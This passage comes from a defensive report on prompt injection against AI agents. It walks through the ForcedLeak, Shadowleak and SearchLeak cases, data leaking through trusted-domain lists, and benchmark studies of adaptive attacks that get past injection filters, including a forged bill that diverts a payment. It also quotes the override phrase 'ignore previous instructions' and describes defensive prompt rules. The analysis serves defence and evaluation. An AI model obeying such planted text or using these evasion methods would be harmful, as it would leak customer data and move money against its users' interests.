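The demonstration's result may depend partly on the employee's request, which Noma also wrote. It asked Agentforce to answer the lead's questions and draft a reply. Such a request is plausible in a sales office, but it in effect asked the agent to act on whatever the form contained, and a request for a short summary might have worked less well. Noma also presents the agent's answer to a question about mixing colours as a sign of weak boundaries, but that is a minor fault next to the agent's ability to read every lead's email address while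 handling a single lead. OWASP would class this access as an excessive permission, and narrowing it would have limited the theft even with the lapsed domain still on the list.

A shorter description field would also have left less room for instructions. Limiting the length of input is an easy form of sanitisation to apply, but a short injection can still do harm, and genuine customers sometimes need to write long descriptions.

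Ravia told The Hacker News (2025) that ForcedLeak was a variant of EchoLeak aimed at Salesforce, and predicted more such flaws in popular agents. The article lists no known victims. Salesforce described its security work to SecurityWeek, in *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft*, but did not say whether anyone had used the flaw before Noma found it. Noma advised customers to search their existing leads for submissions with unusual instructions, since hostile text could already be in a database when an employee asks the agent about it.

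### What Salesforce changed

Salesforce took back the domain and, on 8 September 2025, began enforcing its Trusted URLs list for Agentforce and its Einstein AI services. In an alert quoted by The Hacker News, the company described the list as protection against data escaping "after a successful prompt injection". Like OWASP, Salesforce was planning for some injections to succeed.

The enforcement gave customers more control but also more work. As TechNadu explains in *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*, administrators have to add every outside domain their agents need, or those agents may stop working properly. An administrator who has just broken a colleague's agent is under pressure to approve whatever domains it requests. A broad entry resolves the complaint fastest, but it also gives an attacker the most domains to exploit.

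A later Salesforce guide, *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)*, shows how easily a broad entry can get onto the trusted list. Agentforce Coworker removes web addresses by default, and an administrator adds a trusted address to finish connecting Google Drive. The guide's example is `https://docs.google.com`, where anyone with a Google account can create documents, so the entry covers far more than the company's own files. Whether data could leak through it depends on how the site handles each request, which the administrator would need to find out.

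Salesforce also offers a setting that detects prompt injection. According to PromptArmor, the setting is in beta, and Salesforce appears to train AI on the data of customers who turn it on.

Copilot Studio, Microsoft's product for building agents, has a blunter option. Administrators can turn off images and clickable links altogether, according to Microsoft's *Control image rendering and embedded URLs*. Users lose some convenience, but nobody has to maintain a list for that channel. Willison argues that the route by which data leaves is generally the easiest part of such an attack to remove, and both 2025 cases support this. Neither vendor could reliably recognise a hostile email or form, but removing images from answers would have prevented automatic leaks through images.

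### How to maintain a list of permitted destinations

Microsoft's list included a domain that could relay data, and Salesforce's included one the company no longer owned. A reviewer would have seen familiar company names on either list, so a company has to check separately what each domain does and who controls it.

A domain's ownership can also change after the review. `my-salesforce-cms.com` was presumably a reasonable entry while Salesforce owned it, and the list stayed the same when the registration lapsed. This resembles tool-call drift, and version pinning would not detect it either, because a hash of the list would have matched the approved copy throughout.

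The table lists four ways a permitted destination can fail and a check for each. The last row is based on a 2026 finding in Agentforce.

| Weakness | Example | Check |
|---|---|---|
| The domain forwards requests | Microsoft's Teams service | Try to reach a test server through it |
| The registration lapses | `my-salesforce-cms.com` | Track the renewal date and the registered owner |
| Outsiders can rent space on the domain | `*.amazonaws.com` on Salesforce's list | Permit only the company's own address there |
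| Data leaves by a channel the list does not cover | Email from Agentforce | Restrict recipients and the records the agent can read |

The asterisk in `*.amazonaws.com` is a wildcard that permits every address ending in that name. Amazon rents storage and computing to the public under such addresses, so an attacker might not have needed the lapsed domain. Salesforce's list also had a wildcard for Cloudinary, which hosts images for its customers.

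Each entry needs an owner, a person or team who can explain why it is there and remove it when that reason no longer applies. Both published lists look as if several teams added to them and nobody cleaned them up. The copy in Ravia's report has 43 entries, 14 of which repeat earlier ones, and Salesforce's has several domains with "dev" in their names. This clutter makes a bad entry harder to notice, though it doesn't prove that there is a security hole.

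An expiry check is simple to automate, because the company can look up when each domain registration runs out. When a company retires a domain, it should remove the domain from every list before letting the registration lapse. For suppliers' domains, the owner of the list entry can set a review date and remove the entry then unless someone still needs it.

Testing the list of permitted domains is easier than testing a filter, because the tester can assume that the attacker has already fooled the model. In a test copy of the support assistant, the tester would insert an image directly into an answer, put a made-up customer number in the image's address, and try to get that number to an outside server through each permitted domain. A tester who knew to look for forwarding services could have found the Teams route this way. The company should repeat the test on a schedule and after each new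 entry, because a supplier can add a forwarding service to a permitted domain at any time. These checks take little effort while the list is short, so the build phase is a good time to start them.

### Routes that a browser's list does not cover

A Content Security Policy only governs what the browser fetches. Some assistants fetch web pages through the vendor's servers, where the policy has no effect. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* describes Shadowleak, an attack of this kind on ChatGPT's Deep Research feature when a user had connected it to Gmail. Hidden instructions in an email made the agent find private data in the inbox and visit a web address containing that data. The researchers who found the attack reported that it succeeded in all their repeated tests. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so the employer's monitoring of browsers and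 laptops could miss it.

OpenAI has since adopted a check that does not depend on trusted domains. As Gend summarises it, an agent automatically fetches a web address only if an independent index of the public web already includes that exact address. An address containing a customer's private details would normally be absent from the index, so the user gets a warning and decides whether to continue. OpenAI objects to lists of trusted sites because such sites can redirect visitors elsewhere, and because frequent warnings teach people to click through them. Its own check still relies on the user's judgement when an address is not in the index.

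### Similar flaws in 2026, and criminal use

In April 2026, OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce AI* (2026) reported that Capsule Security had found similar injection flaws in Agentforce and Copilot Studio, both involving forms. Salesforce's weak point was again a public lead form. This time the agent sent the data out by email, according to Security Boulevard's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026). A list of permitted web addresses does not restrict who receives an email.

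In this case, restricting `send_email` to the person who opened the ticket may not be enough, because the attacker may be that person and could then receive another customer's record as a reply. To prevent that, the company also has to restrict `lookup_customer` to the ticket author's own record.

In June, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described another chain of flaws in Microsoft 365 Copilot. The attack started when an employee clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft domain. It combined an injection with two older kinds of web security bug, one of which made a server send a request for the attacker, the same type of weakness as the Teams relay in EchoLeak. The Hacker News reported in *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) that Microsoft rated the flaw critical and mitigated it.

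In July, Underhill (2026) reported in *Azure DevOps Prompt Injection Targets AI Coding Agents* that hidden instructions in Azure DevOps, Microsoft's service for storing and reviewing code, could make a coding agent open sensitive data with a developer's permissions. As with the support worker, running the agent under the user's own identity gives little protection.

Researchers found all these flaws, and the reports describe what an attacker could have done. They do not establish that criminals have stolen company data through indirect injection. The lack of known victims is weak evidence that no thefts occurred, because an employee who sees a broken image has no reason to report it, and a request from the vendor's servers may leave no trace in the company's records. To find a past theft, a company would need logs that link the text the assistant read to the web addresses it produced.

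## Input filters tested against attackers who adapt

EchoLeak showed that an attacker can get past a trained classifier, and researchers have since measured how often attacks get past several widely available filters. Most filters do well against a fixed list of attacks but noticeably worse when the attacker can revise failed attempts. Some also remove a good deal of harmless text, and a company will notice this long before it notices a missed attack.

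### Four ways to treat untrusted text

The simplest method is pattern matching. Software compares incoming text with a list of forbidden phrases, often written as regular expressions (formulas that each match many similar strings), and blocks any match. For the support assistant, one pattern could catch "ignore previous instructions" in any mix of capitals and spacing. The check is fast and always gives the same result for the same text, but, as David C warned, attackers can reword their instructions to avoid a match.

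Developers build a trained classifier by training a small language model on harmless texts and known injections until it can score how closely a new text resembles an injection. They then choose a threshold; a lower one catches more attacks but also flags more honest customers. ProtectAI's detector, Meta's PromptGuard and the academic PIGuard all work this way. Google sells a filter called Model Armor for the same purpose but keeps its design private. When a score exceeds the threshold, the surrounding software can stop the agent, reject the document, or cut out the offending sentences. Cutting sentences keeps more of a ticket but may remove details such as the order number.

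In the third method, a second language model rewrites the text. One such model, DataFilter, receives the user's request and the tool's output, removes anything it classifies as an injected instruction, and returns the rest. The request gives it context that a sentence-by-sentence classifier lacks. But the second model also processes the hostile text, and Narisetty and colleagues point out that screening models are vulnerable to prompt injection like any other model.

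The last method, marking, keeps all of the original text. In spotlighting, the software puts delimiters around each tool result, and the system instructions tell the model not to obey anything between them. One variant, sandwiching, repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, and another puts a warning before it. All three depend on the model ignoring instructions in the untrusted text.

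Ticket 4812 would probably pass a pattern list, since a paragraph headed "Support policy" need not contain any stock phrase. Experiments are needed to determine whether it would pass the other three.

### The AgentDojo benchmark

Many of those experiments use *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), a test environment for agents that read untrusted data. It simulates an office workspace, a Slack messaging account, a travel agency and a bank. The agent receives an ordinary request, such as paying a bill, and tools that read and change the simulated accounts. The attacker's text appears where an outsider could have written it, such as in an email or on a web page.

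The benchmark's first version has 97 user tasks and 27 attacker goals. Each security case pairs one task with one goal from the same environment, which gives 240 cases for workspace (40 × 6), 105 for Slack (21 × 5), 140 for travel (20 × 7) and 144 for banking (16 × 9), or 629 in total. The benchmark has grown since, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) puts it at over 900 pairings.

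AgentDojo produces three scores. Benign utility is the share of user tasks the agent completes when nobody attacks. The attack success rate is the share of security cases in which the agent does what the attacker wanted. Utility under attack is the share of security cases in which the agent completes the user's task with no harmful side effects. Ordinary code computes all three by inspecting the accounts afterwards, for example checking whether money went to the attacker. Debenedetti and colleagues avoided using a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge.

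Attack success rates on this test are more useful for comparing the same agent with and without a defence than for predicting how often attacks would succeed at a real company. Researchers chose the tasks and the goals, and some pairs are much easier to attack than others, so a rate of 5% doesn't mean that one hostile email in twenty would succeed in practice.

The benchmark comes with a few fixed attacks, and its creators warned that it is easy to build a defence that stops a particular attack. They meant other researchers to add new attacks aimed at each defence, but many didn't. As late as November 2026, *AutoPI* (2026) noted that most reported success rates still came from fixed sets of attacks. The other problem with filters also appeared in the original tests, where ProtectAI's detector raised so many false alarms that the agent completed far fewer of its users' tasks.

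### Twelve defences against determined attackers

In October 2025, researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and several other institutions tested twelve published defences against attackers who knew the defence and had time to work on it (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, *The Attacker Moves Second*). The original evaluations reported attack success near zero for most of these defences. Some were meant to stop jailbreaks, where users try to get forbidden content out of a model. The others were meant to stop prompt injection, and they included Model Armor, spotlighting and all three of the classifiers above.

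The researchers used four kinds of attacker, all of which repeat a cycle of proposing a text, scoring the result, keeping the best attempts and revising them:

- Gradient methods calculate from a model's internal numbers which changes to the text should help.
- Reinforcement learning trains an attacking model by rewarding it for attempts that get closer to the goal.
- Search methods have a language model rewrite the most promising earlier attempts.
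- Human attackers, more than 500 of them, competed online for $20,000 in prizes.

The team chose methods that seemed likely to work on each defence, and its attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve. Zhan, Fang and colleagues had already bypassed eight defences, with success rates above 50%, in *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents*.

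The table gives the search attacker's results on AgentDojo when the agent ran on Gemini 2.5 Pro. The last column is the median number of tries before the first success, leaving out cases where the attacker never succeeded.

| Defence | Fixed attack succeeds | Adaptive attack succeeds | User tasks completed | Median tries |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 74% | 13 |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 75% | 14 |
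| PromptGuard | 26% | 94% | 72% | 21 |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 59% | 22 |
| ProtectAI | 15% | 90% | 39% | 30 |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 39% | 46 |

PIGuard resisted best, but with it the agent completed only about half as many tasks as without a filter. PromptGuard and spotlighting barely reduced the agent's usefulness but gave little protection, even against the fixed attack. ProtectAI's detector blocked some thefts only because it mistook the secret the attacker wanted for an attack and deleted it, so the researchers left those cases out of its score.

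Many of the successful texts looked like ordinary office notes, with no visible attempt to override the user. Nasr and colleagues conclude that a detector could catch such notes only by also flagging many more harmless ones. Stacking several detectors didn't solve the problem either.

These conditions favoured the attacker. The search attacker could see the detector's confidence score after each attempt and had up to 800 tries per case, on a sample of 80 cases. The researchers say they wanted to know whether a defence could hold, not how much effort it would take to break. Results also depended on the model behind the filter. With GPT-5 Mini, the same attacker succeeded against PIGuard in 49% of cases. However, the automated attacker was not the strongest available. It succeeded in 69% of 29 scenarios that it and the human contestants both attempted, while at least one person succeeded in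 every scenario.

### AutoDojo: six revisions and very little feedback

Few real attackers can see a filter's confidence score, so *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives its attacker much less information. The attacker can place text where the agent will read it and can tell whether the attack worked, but cannot see the filter, the agent's reasoning or the user's request. Someone who sends tickets to the support assistant and waits to see whether a stolen record arrives is in about the same position.

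AutoDojo starts by inserting each of a set of known attacks into the same harmless document. Several user requests may lead an agent to read that document, and an attack's score is the number of those requests in which the agent carries out the attacker's goal. If five requests involve reading the same hotel review and the agent obeys the hidden text in two of them, that text scores 2. Scoring across requests makes sense because a real attacker plants one text without knowing what the next employee will ask.

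Gemini 3.1 Pro, a language model, then receives the five best attempts with their scores. It first writes a diagnosis of why some worked and what sort of defence might be in place, then writes one new version. The program tests this version and adds it to the ranking. After six rounds, the program returns the best of the newly written texts. The procedure needs no training and no access to the target model's internals, only a subscription to a good commercial model.

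The researchers ran this against five models and ten defences: two kinds of marking, four filters and four policy layers. They used 389 of AgentDojo's security cases, leaving out the workspace environment because agents there often completed neither the user's task nor the attacker's. The next table shows the marking and filter results for an agent running on GPT-4o-mini.

| Defence | Fixed attack succeeds | AutoDojo succeeds | User tasks completed |
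|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58.6% | 52.4% | 66.7% |
| Warning before tool output | 39.3% | 40.4% | 68.4% |
| Spotlighting | 51.7% | 46.8% | 59.6% |
| PromptGuard | 54.2% | 49.4% | 63.2% |
| PIGuard | 0.0% | 28.0% | 43.9% |
| ProtectAI | 7.2% | 15.4% | 47.4% |
| DataFilter | 12.6% | 33.4% | 64.9% |

After six rounds of revision, more than a quarter of the attacks succeeded against PIGuard, which looked like a complete solution in the first column. The success rate rose from 12.6% to 33.4% against DataFilter and roughly doubled against ProtectAI, from about 28 cases to 60.

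The filters look better when compared with the top row, which has no defence. PIGuard still cut the adaptive attacker's success by almost half, ProtectAI by about 70%, and DataFilter by a little over a third. DataFilter may offer the best trade-off in the table, since it lowered the agent's utility by less than two points. PIGuard and ProtectAI each lowered it by around 20 points because they removed sentences the agent needed.

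(AutoDojo does worse than the fixed attack in some rows because the researchers required it to return a new text. Its subtler wording is less effective than a blunt command when nothing is there to block the command. A real attacker could simply use whichever works.)

The increases were smaller on other models. AutoDojo succeeded against PIGuard in 10.5% of cases with DeepSeek-v4-Flash, 4.6% with Gemini 2.5 Flash and 0.8% with Claude Haiku 4.5. But attacks on Haiku succeeded in only 1.8% of cases without a filter, so adding PIGuard lowered attack success by just one percentage point. It also reduced Haiku's completed tasks by almost a third, from 70.2% to 47.4%. Whether a filter is worth having depends heavily on the model behind it, so a vendor's figures for one model may mislead a customer who uses another.

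Filters can reduce task completion far more on unfamiliar work. Ma and colleagues repeated the tests on AgentDyn, a second benchmark with tasks in coding, shopping and everyday errands. The GPT-4o-mini agent completed 46.7% of these tasks with no defence and 1.7% with ProtectAI. The policy layers generally resisted AutoDojo better than the filters did, though they had drawbacks of their own.

More rounds of revision helped the attacker only modestly. Against PIGuard on GPT-4o-mini, attacks succeeded 26.0% of the time after two rounds and 30.8% after twelve. Telling the attacker why each attempt had failed, including PIGuard's scores, lowered success to 23.4%, because the attacker then wrote texts that passed the filter but no longer persuaded the agent. Keeping the choice of filter secret is therefore unlikely to keep a company safe.

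All these figures come from single runs without error bars, so differences of a few points between defences mean little. They also can't be compared directly with the 71% that Nasr and colleagues reached against PIGuard, because the two studies used different models, cases and budgets.

### Why loosely worded requests are the most exposed

Ma and colleagues also sorted the user tasks by how much each request left to outside text. Some requests include every detail, such as a change of address that gives the new address. Others name an action but leave the details to a document, such as paying the bill in a certain file. The most open-ended requests leave even the choice of actions to the outside text, such as a request to do everything on a to-do list at a web address.

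On GPT-4o-mini, AutoDojo's success rose steeply with looseness.

| Filter | Everything stated | Details left open | Action left open |
|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | 17.3% | 31.1% | 54.2% |
| ProtectAI | 3.9% | 18.5% | 45.8% |
| DataFilter | 20.5% | 38.2% | 54.2% |

This happens because these filters look for text that resembles an instruction to the model, and an attacker doesn't need one when the user's request is loose. In one of the banking cases, the user asked the agent to pay a bill stored in a file, and the attacker wanted the money sent elsewhere. The fixed attack put a message to the AI assistant inside the bill, and PIGuard removed nearly all of it. AutoDojo's version looked like part of the bill, with a payee, an amount and a notice that the payment details had changed. PIGuard removed none of it. The agent paid the attacker and told the user that the bill was settled.

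An honest supplier that changes banks sends much the same notice as a fraudster. A classifier can't learn to tell the two notices apart from their wording, because they differ in who owns the account. Accounts departments have long dealt with this kind of fraud by checking new payment details against a record they already trust, and an agent's software can do the same.

Filtering out instructions hardly makes sense when the user's request leaves the action itself open. A to-do list, for example, consists of instructions that the user wants the agent to follow. To remove only the attacker's entry, a filter would have to identify who wrote each one.

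The evidence for the loosest group is thin, with 24 security cases from only four user tasks, so 54.2% means 13 cases. The researchers assigned tasks to groups by hand and admit that others might sort some of them differently. AgentDyn has 114 such cases, and its results support the finding. PIGuard's figures there on GPT-4o-mini were 26.3% for the loosest requests and 5.5% for the fully stated ones. However, in AgentDyn's everyday-errands environment, the undefended agent was about equally exposed whatever the wording.

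If an employee tells the support assistant to "deal with ticket 4812", the person who wrote the ticket can decide nearly everything the assistant does. That person has much less control if the employee asks it to "tell this customer when the order will arrive". Noma's ForcedLeak demonstration relied on a broad request like the first. A company could build narrower requests into buttons, so that employees don't have to think about wording.

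### False alarms in a company's daily traffic

When hostile documents are rare, most of the documents a filter flags can be harmless, even if its error rates are low. Take a hypothetical agent that reads 100,000 documents in a month, 10 of them hostile. A filter that detects 99% of attacks and wrongly flags 1% of harmless text, which would be an excellent result in most of the tests above, would flag about 1,000 harmless documents along with the 10 or so hostile ones.

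- Hostile documents caught: 10 × 0.99 = 9.9, or about 10.
- Harmless documents blocked: 99,990 × 0.01 = 999.9, or about 1,000.

Only about one alarm in a hundred is real. Reviewing a month's alarms at five minutes each takes 84 hours, and a reviewer who has just released 99 harmless documents is likely to release the next one too. If nobody reviews the alarms, a thousand customers and colleagues get no answer or an incomplete one. Raising the detection rate to 100% would catch an average of 0.1 more malicious documents a month. Cutting the false-alarm rate to 0.1% would prevent 900 false alarms, so a buyer should ask about that rate first.

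The buyer also needs to know whether the false-alarm rate applies to a whole document or to one piece of it. Many detectors split a document into short overlapping pieces and flag the whole document if any piece looks hostile. *Defusing Explosive Prompts* (2026) gives the chance of flagging a harmless document as 1 − (1 − *p*)^*N*, where *p* is the false-alarm rate per piece, *N* is the number of pieces, and the pieces are treated as independent. At a rate of 1% per piece, a harmless document with 20 pieces gets flagged 18% of the time, and a 2,000-word document with 402 overlapping pieces gets flagged 98% of the time. To reduce the longer document's rate to 1%, the detector could wrongly flag only about one piece in 40,000.

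A filter's threshold can be badly set for long documents. *LongPIBench* (2026) tested nine detectors against one type of attack. When the task was to summarise emails, the first version of Meta's Prompt Guard flagged 1% of harmless inputs and missed 98% of attacks. Version 2 caught every attack, but flagged 95% of harmless inputs. Two other detectors flagged everything, and two flagged nothing. A different threshold might help in some cases, but the company has to find it using its own documents.

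Text about attacks is especially hard to classify. According to *The Mirror Design Pattern* (2026), a small version of Prompt Guard 2 flagged 21.3% of 2,386 harmless security documents, such as white papers that quote or discuss injections. A customer who pastes a suspicious message into a ticket to ask whether it is genuine would run into the same problem.

### Nine ways to protect three secrets

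Filters can also check a model's output. In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (April 2026), Deep, Emmons and colleagues compared nine configurations across more than 20,000 attacks and found that only those that checked the model's output had no leaks.

They put three secrets in a model's system instructions: an authentication token, a database identifier and an escalation code. An attacking model then tried to extract them by messaging the target directly. It sent ten messages per round and used the replies to rewrite its five best attempts for the next round. Both models were Gemini 2.5 Pro with safety filters off. Each secret in a reply added 0.30 to a leak score capped at 1. The chatbot's name added 0.10, and each run of seven or more words copied from the instructions added 0.05.

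After 25 rounds, most of the defences still seemed to be working. The researchers then continued testing each one until it reached a score of 0.9, the value of all three secrets, or until round 500. The input filter, which combined regular expressions with a classifier run by Gemini, failed first, in round 39. A plain rule in the system instructions never to reveal credentials lasted until round 49, and tags around the user's text until round 84. Telling the model to rank its own instructions above the user's held until round 247, and repeating the security rules after the user's text held until round 277. The order could well change in a second run, but all five defences would have passed a short test. For a long time the attacker got nothing or only harmless fragments, and then obtained almost everything in one round.

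The output check is a few lines of ordinary code that compare each reply with the system instructions and block it if the two share any text. Deep and colleagues report no leaks in 15,000 attacks on the two configurations that included it. (They describe six runs of 5,000 attacks, which would total 30,000.) They attribute the difference to the code having only a few known strings to look for, whereas an attacker can phrase a request in endless ways.

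The check and the scoring both match only exact text, so a secret that came out encoded, or spelled one letter at a time, would have passed the check and been scored as no leak. The researchers acknowledge this gap. Zero recorded leaks is therefore close to what one would expect from the design, although it does confirm that no plain copy got through.

The other defences also did better together than the headline implies. With all of them on except the output check, 23 of 5,000 attacks leaked something, but none revealed a whole secret, because the worst score was 0.10 and a single secret is worth 0.30. Most of the researchers work for Swept AI, which sells security testing, and the paper recommends the company's product.

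Secrets in a prompt are also unusually easy to guard, because the company knows them in advance and no legitimate reply ever needs to contain them. A customer's record, by contrast, belongs in an email to that customer and nowhere else, so the code would have to check the recipient as well as the text. The researchers, like OWASP, advise keeping passwords and tokens out of the prompt altogether.

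### The case for keeping a filter

Defenders of filters reply that most attackers are not research teams. Even Nasr and colleagues, who report the harshest results, call detectors useful because they are easy to deploy and stop some unsophisticated attacks. Such attacks also occur outside laboratories, and *BrowseSafe++* (2026) includes 32,187 test pages built from injections found on live websites. Text planted on a public page for any agent to read is more like the fixed attacks in these experiments than the adaptive ones, and PIGuard blocked every fixed attack in the three AgentDojo environments tested. In the same research, however, an automated attacker that revised the injections using feedback from the target agents reached an average success rate of 78.79%.

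It also found that some models can recognise an injection when asked to look for one, but still follow the same injection while doing a task. This is a reason to use a separate program for detection instead of relying on the agent.

Filters also force attackers to make more attempts. Against Gemini 2.5 Pro, the median number of tries before a first success rose from 13 with no defence to 46 with PIGuard. That increase is trivial for a computer, but an attacker who has to submit each attempt as a support ticket would send dozens of strange tickets from one source, giving the company time to notice if anyone reads the alerts. The attacker can avoid some of this exposure by practising first on a copy of the filter, since ProtectAI's detector and PromptGuard are free to download. A privately adjusted filter or a closed service is harder to practise against, but AutoDojo made progress without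 any knowledge of the filter.

Developers can retrain a classifier on the attacks that beat it, and Ma and colleagues consider this worthwhile. But the attacker can then run the same six rounds against the new version. A company that relies on retraining has to repeat it regularly, and will usually be responding to attacks that have already happened.

Before switching on a filter, a company can run it on a month of old tickets and count how many harmless ones it would have blocked. This takes a day or two and requires no sample attacks. The result may justify sending flagged tickets to the support worker instead of blocking them, and having the assistant handle them without `lookup_customer` or `send_email`. A false alarm then means a few minutes of manual work for an employee, and the customer still gets an answer.

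## How well current models resist injection by themselves

A company would need filters less if the model ignored planted instructions. Developers now train models to do this, and the best models of late 2026 resist most of the attacks in published tests. The attacks that still succeed tend to cluster in a few situations, and a company can't tell from a low average success rate whether its own system is in one of those situations.

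### How developers train models to ignore planted commands

Developers train models to rank instructions by source and to treat a command inside a document as part of the document. The ranking OpenAI published for its gpt-oss models, for example, puts tool results last. To train both behaviors, the developer gives the model many conversations that contain conflicting instructions and rewards it for following the right one. If one of these conversations included ticket 4812 with its hidden paragraph, the developer would reward the model for answering the complaint about the parcel, but not for emailing another customer's record.

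Training a model to resist injection works best when the examples include attacks that still fool it. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes how the company finds such attacks for Atlas, its web browser with a built-in agent. OpenAI trained a separate language model to write injections. This model sends each draft to a simulator, which returns a prediction of how the browser agent would reason and act, and it revises the draft several times in response. In one attack it found, a planted email made the agent send a resignation letter to the user's CEO when the user had only asked for an out-of-office reply. OpenAI trains the agent on the attacks that worked.

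StruQ and SecAlign, two earlier academic defenses, did badly against attackers who adapted. StruQ trains a model on prompts with planted instructions in the data, and SecAlign trains it to prefer answers that ignore them. The original papers reported attack success near zero for both. Narisetty and colleagues cite later tests in which attackers used the model's internal numbers to improve their text. Attack success rose to 80% to 100% against StruQ and 46% to 88% against SecAlign, depending on the benchmark. Outsiders can't use this technique on a commercial model whose internals are secret, but they can still use trial and error, as AutoDojo does.

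The training can also make a model ignore genuine information. While testing an early version of Claude Opus 4.5, Anthropic gave it invented search results reporting that the company had closed one of its research teams. The model left out the news and wrote a summary from what it already knew. Anthropic found two such omissions and thinks the most likely cause is training that taught the model to ignore suspicious tool results. Anthropic saw no sign of a wider tendency to deceive. A support assistant that did the same might leave out an odd but true statement in a ticket, and the support worker would have no reason to look for it.

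### Claude Opus 4.5 and the persistent attacker

Anthropic released Claude Opus 4.5 in November 2025 and published its results on Agent Red Teaming (ART), a benchmark by the security company Gray Swan. Gray Swan tested the model with attacks that had worked on several AI models in a competition with thousands of participants. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* puts the chance of a successful attack on Opus 4.5 at 4.7% with one attempt, 33.6% within ten and 63% within a hundred.

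Rival models did worse. Bathgate's *Anthropic announces Claude Opus 4.5, the new AI coding frontrunner* reports that single attempts succeeded 12.6% of the time against GPT-5.1 and 12.5% against Gemini 3 Pro. Within a hundred attempts, the success rates rose to 87.8% and 92%, respectively.

Narisetty and colleagues say the Opus 4.5 figures come from coding environments, but ART tests tool use more generally. For coding, Anthropic used Shade, a Gray Swan program that revises its attacks. Shade succeeded against Opus 4.5 on 0.3% of single attempts when the model reasoned at length before acting ("extended thinking") and 0.7% when it did not. Within 200 attempts, the rates were 10.0% and 17.5%, respectively.

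The ART figures rise more slowly than they would if every attempt had the same independent chance of success. With a 4.7% chance each time, an attacker would have a 38% chance of at least one success in ten attempts (1 − 0.953^10) and a 99% chance in a hundred.

The lower measured rates suggest that some cases are much harder to attack than others. They fit well with a simple hypothetical model in which each attempt has a 7.5% chance of success in 63% of cases and no chance in the other 37%.

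| Attempts | Measured | Same chance in every case | 63% vulnerable, 37% immune |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38% | 34% |
| 100 | 63.0% | 99% | 63% |

Cases probably vary in difficulty by degree instead of falling into two groups. Similar attacks may also fail for the same reason, so a second attempt can add little to the chance of success. Even after a hundred attempts fail on a case, the next hundred or a new kind of attack may succeed.

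An attacker can send the support assistant many tickets without success if its set-up is one of the hard cases. If it is one of the vulnerable ones, a hundred tickets will almost certainly be enough, even though any single ticket will probably fail. The company can't tell from the benchmark's average which case applies. An attacker can also spread the attempts out by sending the same text to a hundred companies that use the same model.

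### Claude models in 2026

Claude models did so well on ART that Anthropic stopped reporting it in 2026 and replaced it with the Indirect Prompt Injection (IPI) benchmark. Gray Swan built IPI with several model developers and the UK and US governments' AI testing institutes. The benchmark extends a public attack competition that Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) describe. It has 28 new scenarios in which an attacker tries to cause irreversible harm, such as stealing data or moving money. Gray Swan and its partners kept 1,130 attacks that worked well across different models.

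Anthropic reported in July 2026 that attackers succeeded against Claude Opus 5 on 0.2% of single attempts and 2.0% of the time when allowed fifteen attempts, down from 0.5% and 5.5% for Claude Opus 4.8. The rates for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol were 3.1% and 20.0%. Among models from other developers, Meta's Muse Spark resisted injection best, with attackers succeeding within fifteen attempts 16.5% of the time.

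The hypothetical agent that reads ten hostile documents a month would obey one about every three months at a rate of 3.1% per document, and about one every four years at 0.2%. Both intervals may be too short, because few real hostile documents would be as well written as the benchmark's attacks. But they would be much too long for a company targeted by a determined attacker.

Anthropic also tested Opus 5 against attackers who revised their texts. The table shows the model's results with extended thinking. Each cell gives the share of all attempts that succeeded, then the number of scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeded.

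| Setting | Attempts per scenario | Model alone | With added safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 200 | 0.56%, 13 of 40 | 0.18%, 4 of 40 |
| Controlling a computer's screen | 200 | 0.54%, 1 of 14 | 0.25%, 1 of 14 |
| Web browsing | 10 | 3.70%, 11 of 129 | 0%, 0 of 129 |

The successes were again concentrated in a few scenarios. In the browser test, about 48 of 1,290 attempts succeeded (3.70%), all of them in 11 scenarios. Within those scenarios, more than 40% of attempts succeeded. All the successes in the screen-control test came from a single scenario.

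The newest or most capable model is also not always the most resistant to injection. In the same browser test, with extended thinking and no safeguards, attacks succeeded 29.7% of the time against Claude Mythos 5 and 0.93% of the time against Claude Sonnet 5, a model in a less capable line. For Opus 4.8, extended thinking cut attack success from 17.44% to 7.03% in the coding test, but in the browser test attacks succeeded more often with it (31.5%) than without it (17.8%). A company that upgrades its model or changes how long the model thinks could therefore make its agent easier to attack, and such a change is also a form of tool-call drift.

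Anthropic has since released several models. In its September card for Claude Mythos 5.1, the company calls the model its most robust so far on the IPI benchmark. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, published the same month, reports results similar to or better than those of Opus 5 on every injection test, but warns that the model is more likely than its predecessors to follow some malicious instructions.

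### FrontierBreach: GPT-6, Gemini 4 and Claude Fable 5.2

OpenAI's results depend heavily on how the attack reaches the model. In its system card for GPT-5.6, OpenAI reported few failures when attackers typed into the chat and more when their text came through tools, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). The result for tools is the relevant one for the support assistant.

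PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* benchmark covers newer models from all three large developers. It adds attacks to tasks from GDPval, OpenAI's collection of professional tasks such as analysing a portfolio of bonds. PromptArmor modelled the attacks on ones its researchers had found, with goals such as stealing data or installing ransomware. Fixed checks determine whether the attacks succeed. All models ran at medium reasoning effort. The table shows some of the 22 results, with 95% confidence intervals.

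| Model | Attack success rate |
|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | 2.4% ± 2.2 |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 4.3% ± 2.9 |
| GPT-6 Astra | 7.6% ± 3.8 |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 10.0% ± 4.2 |
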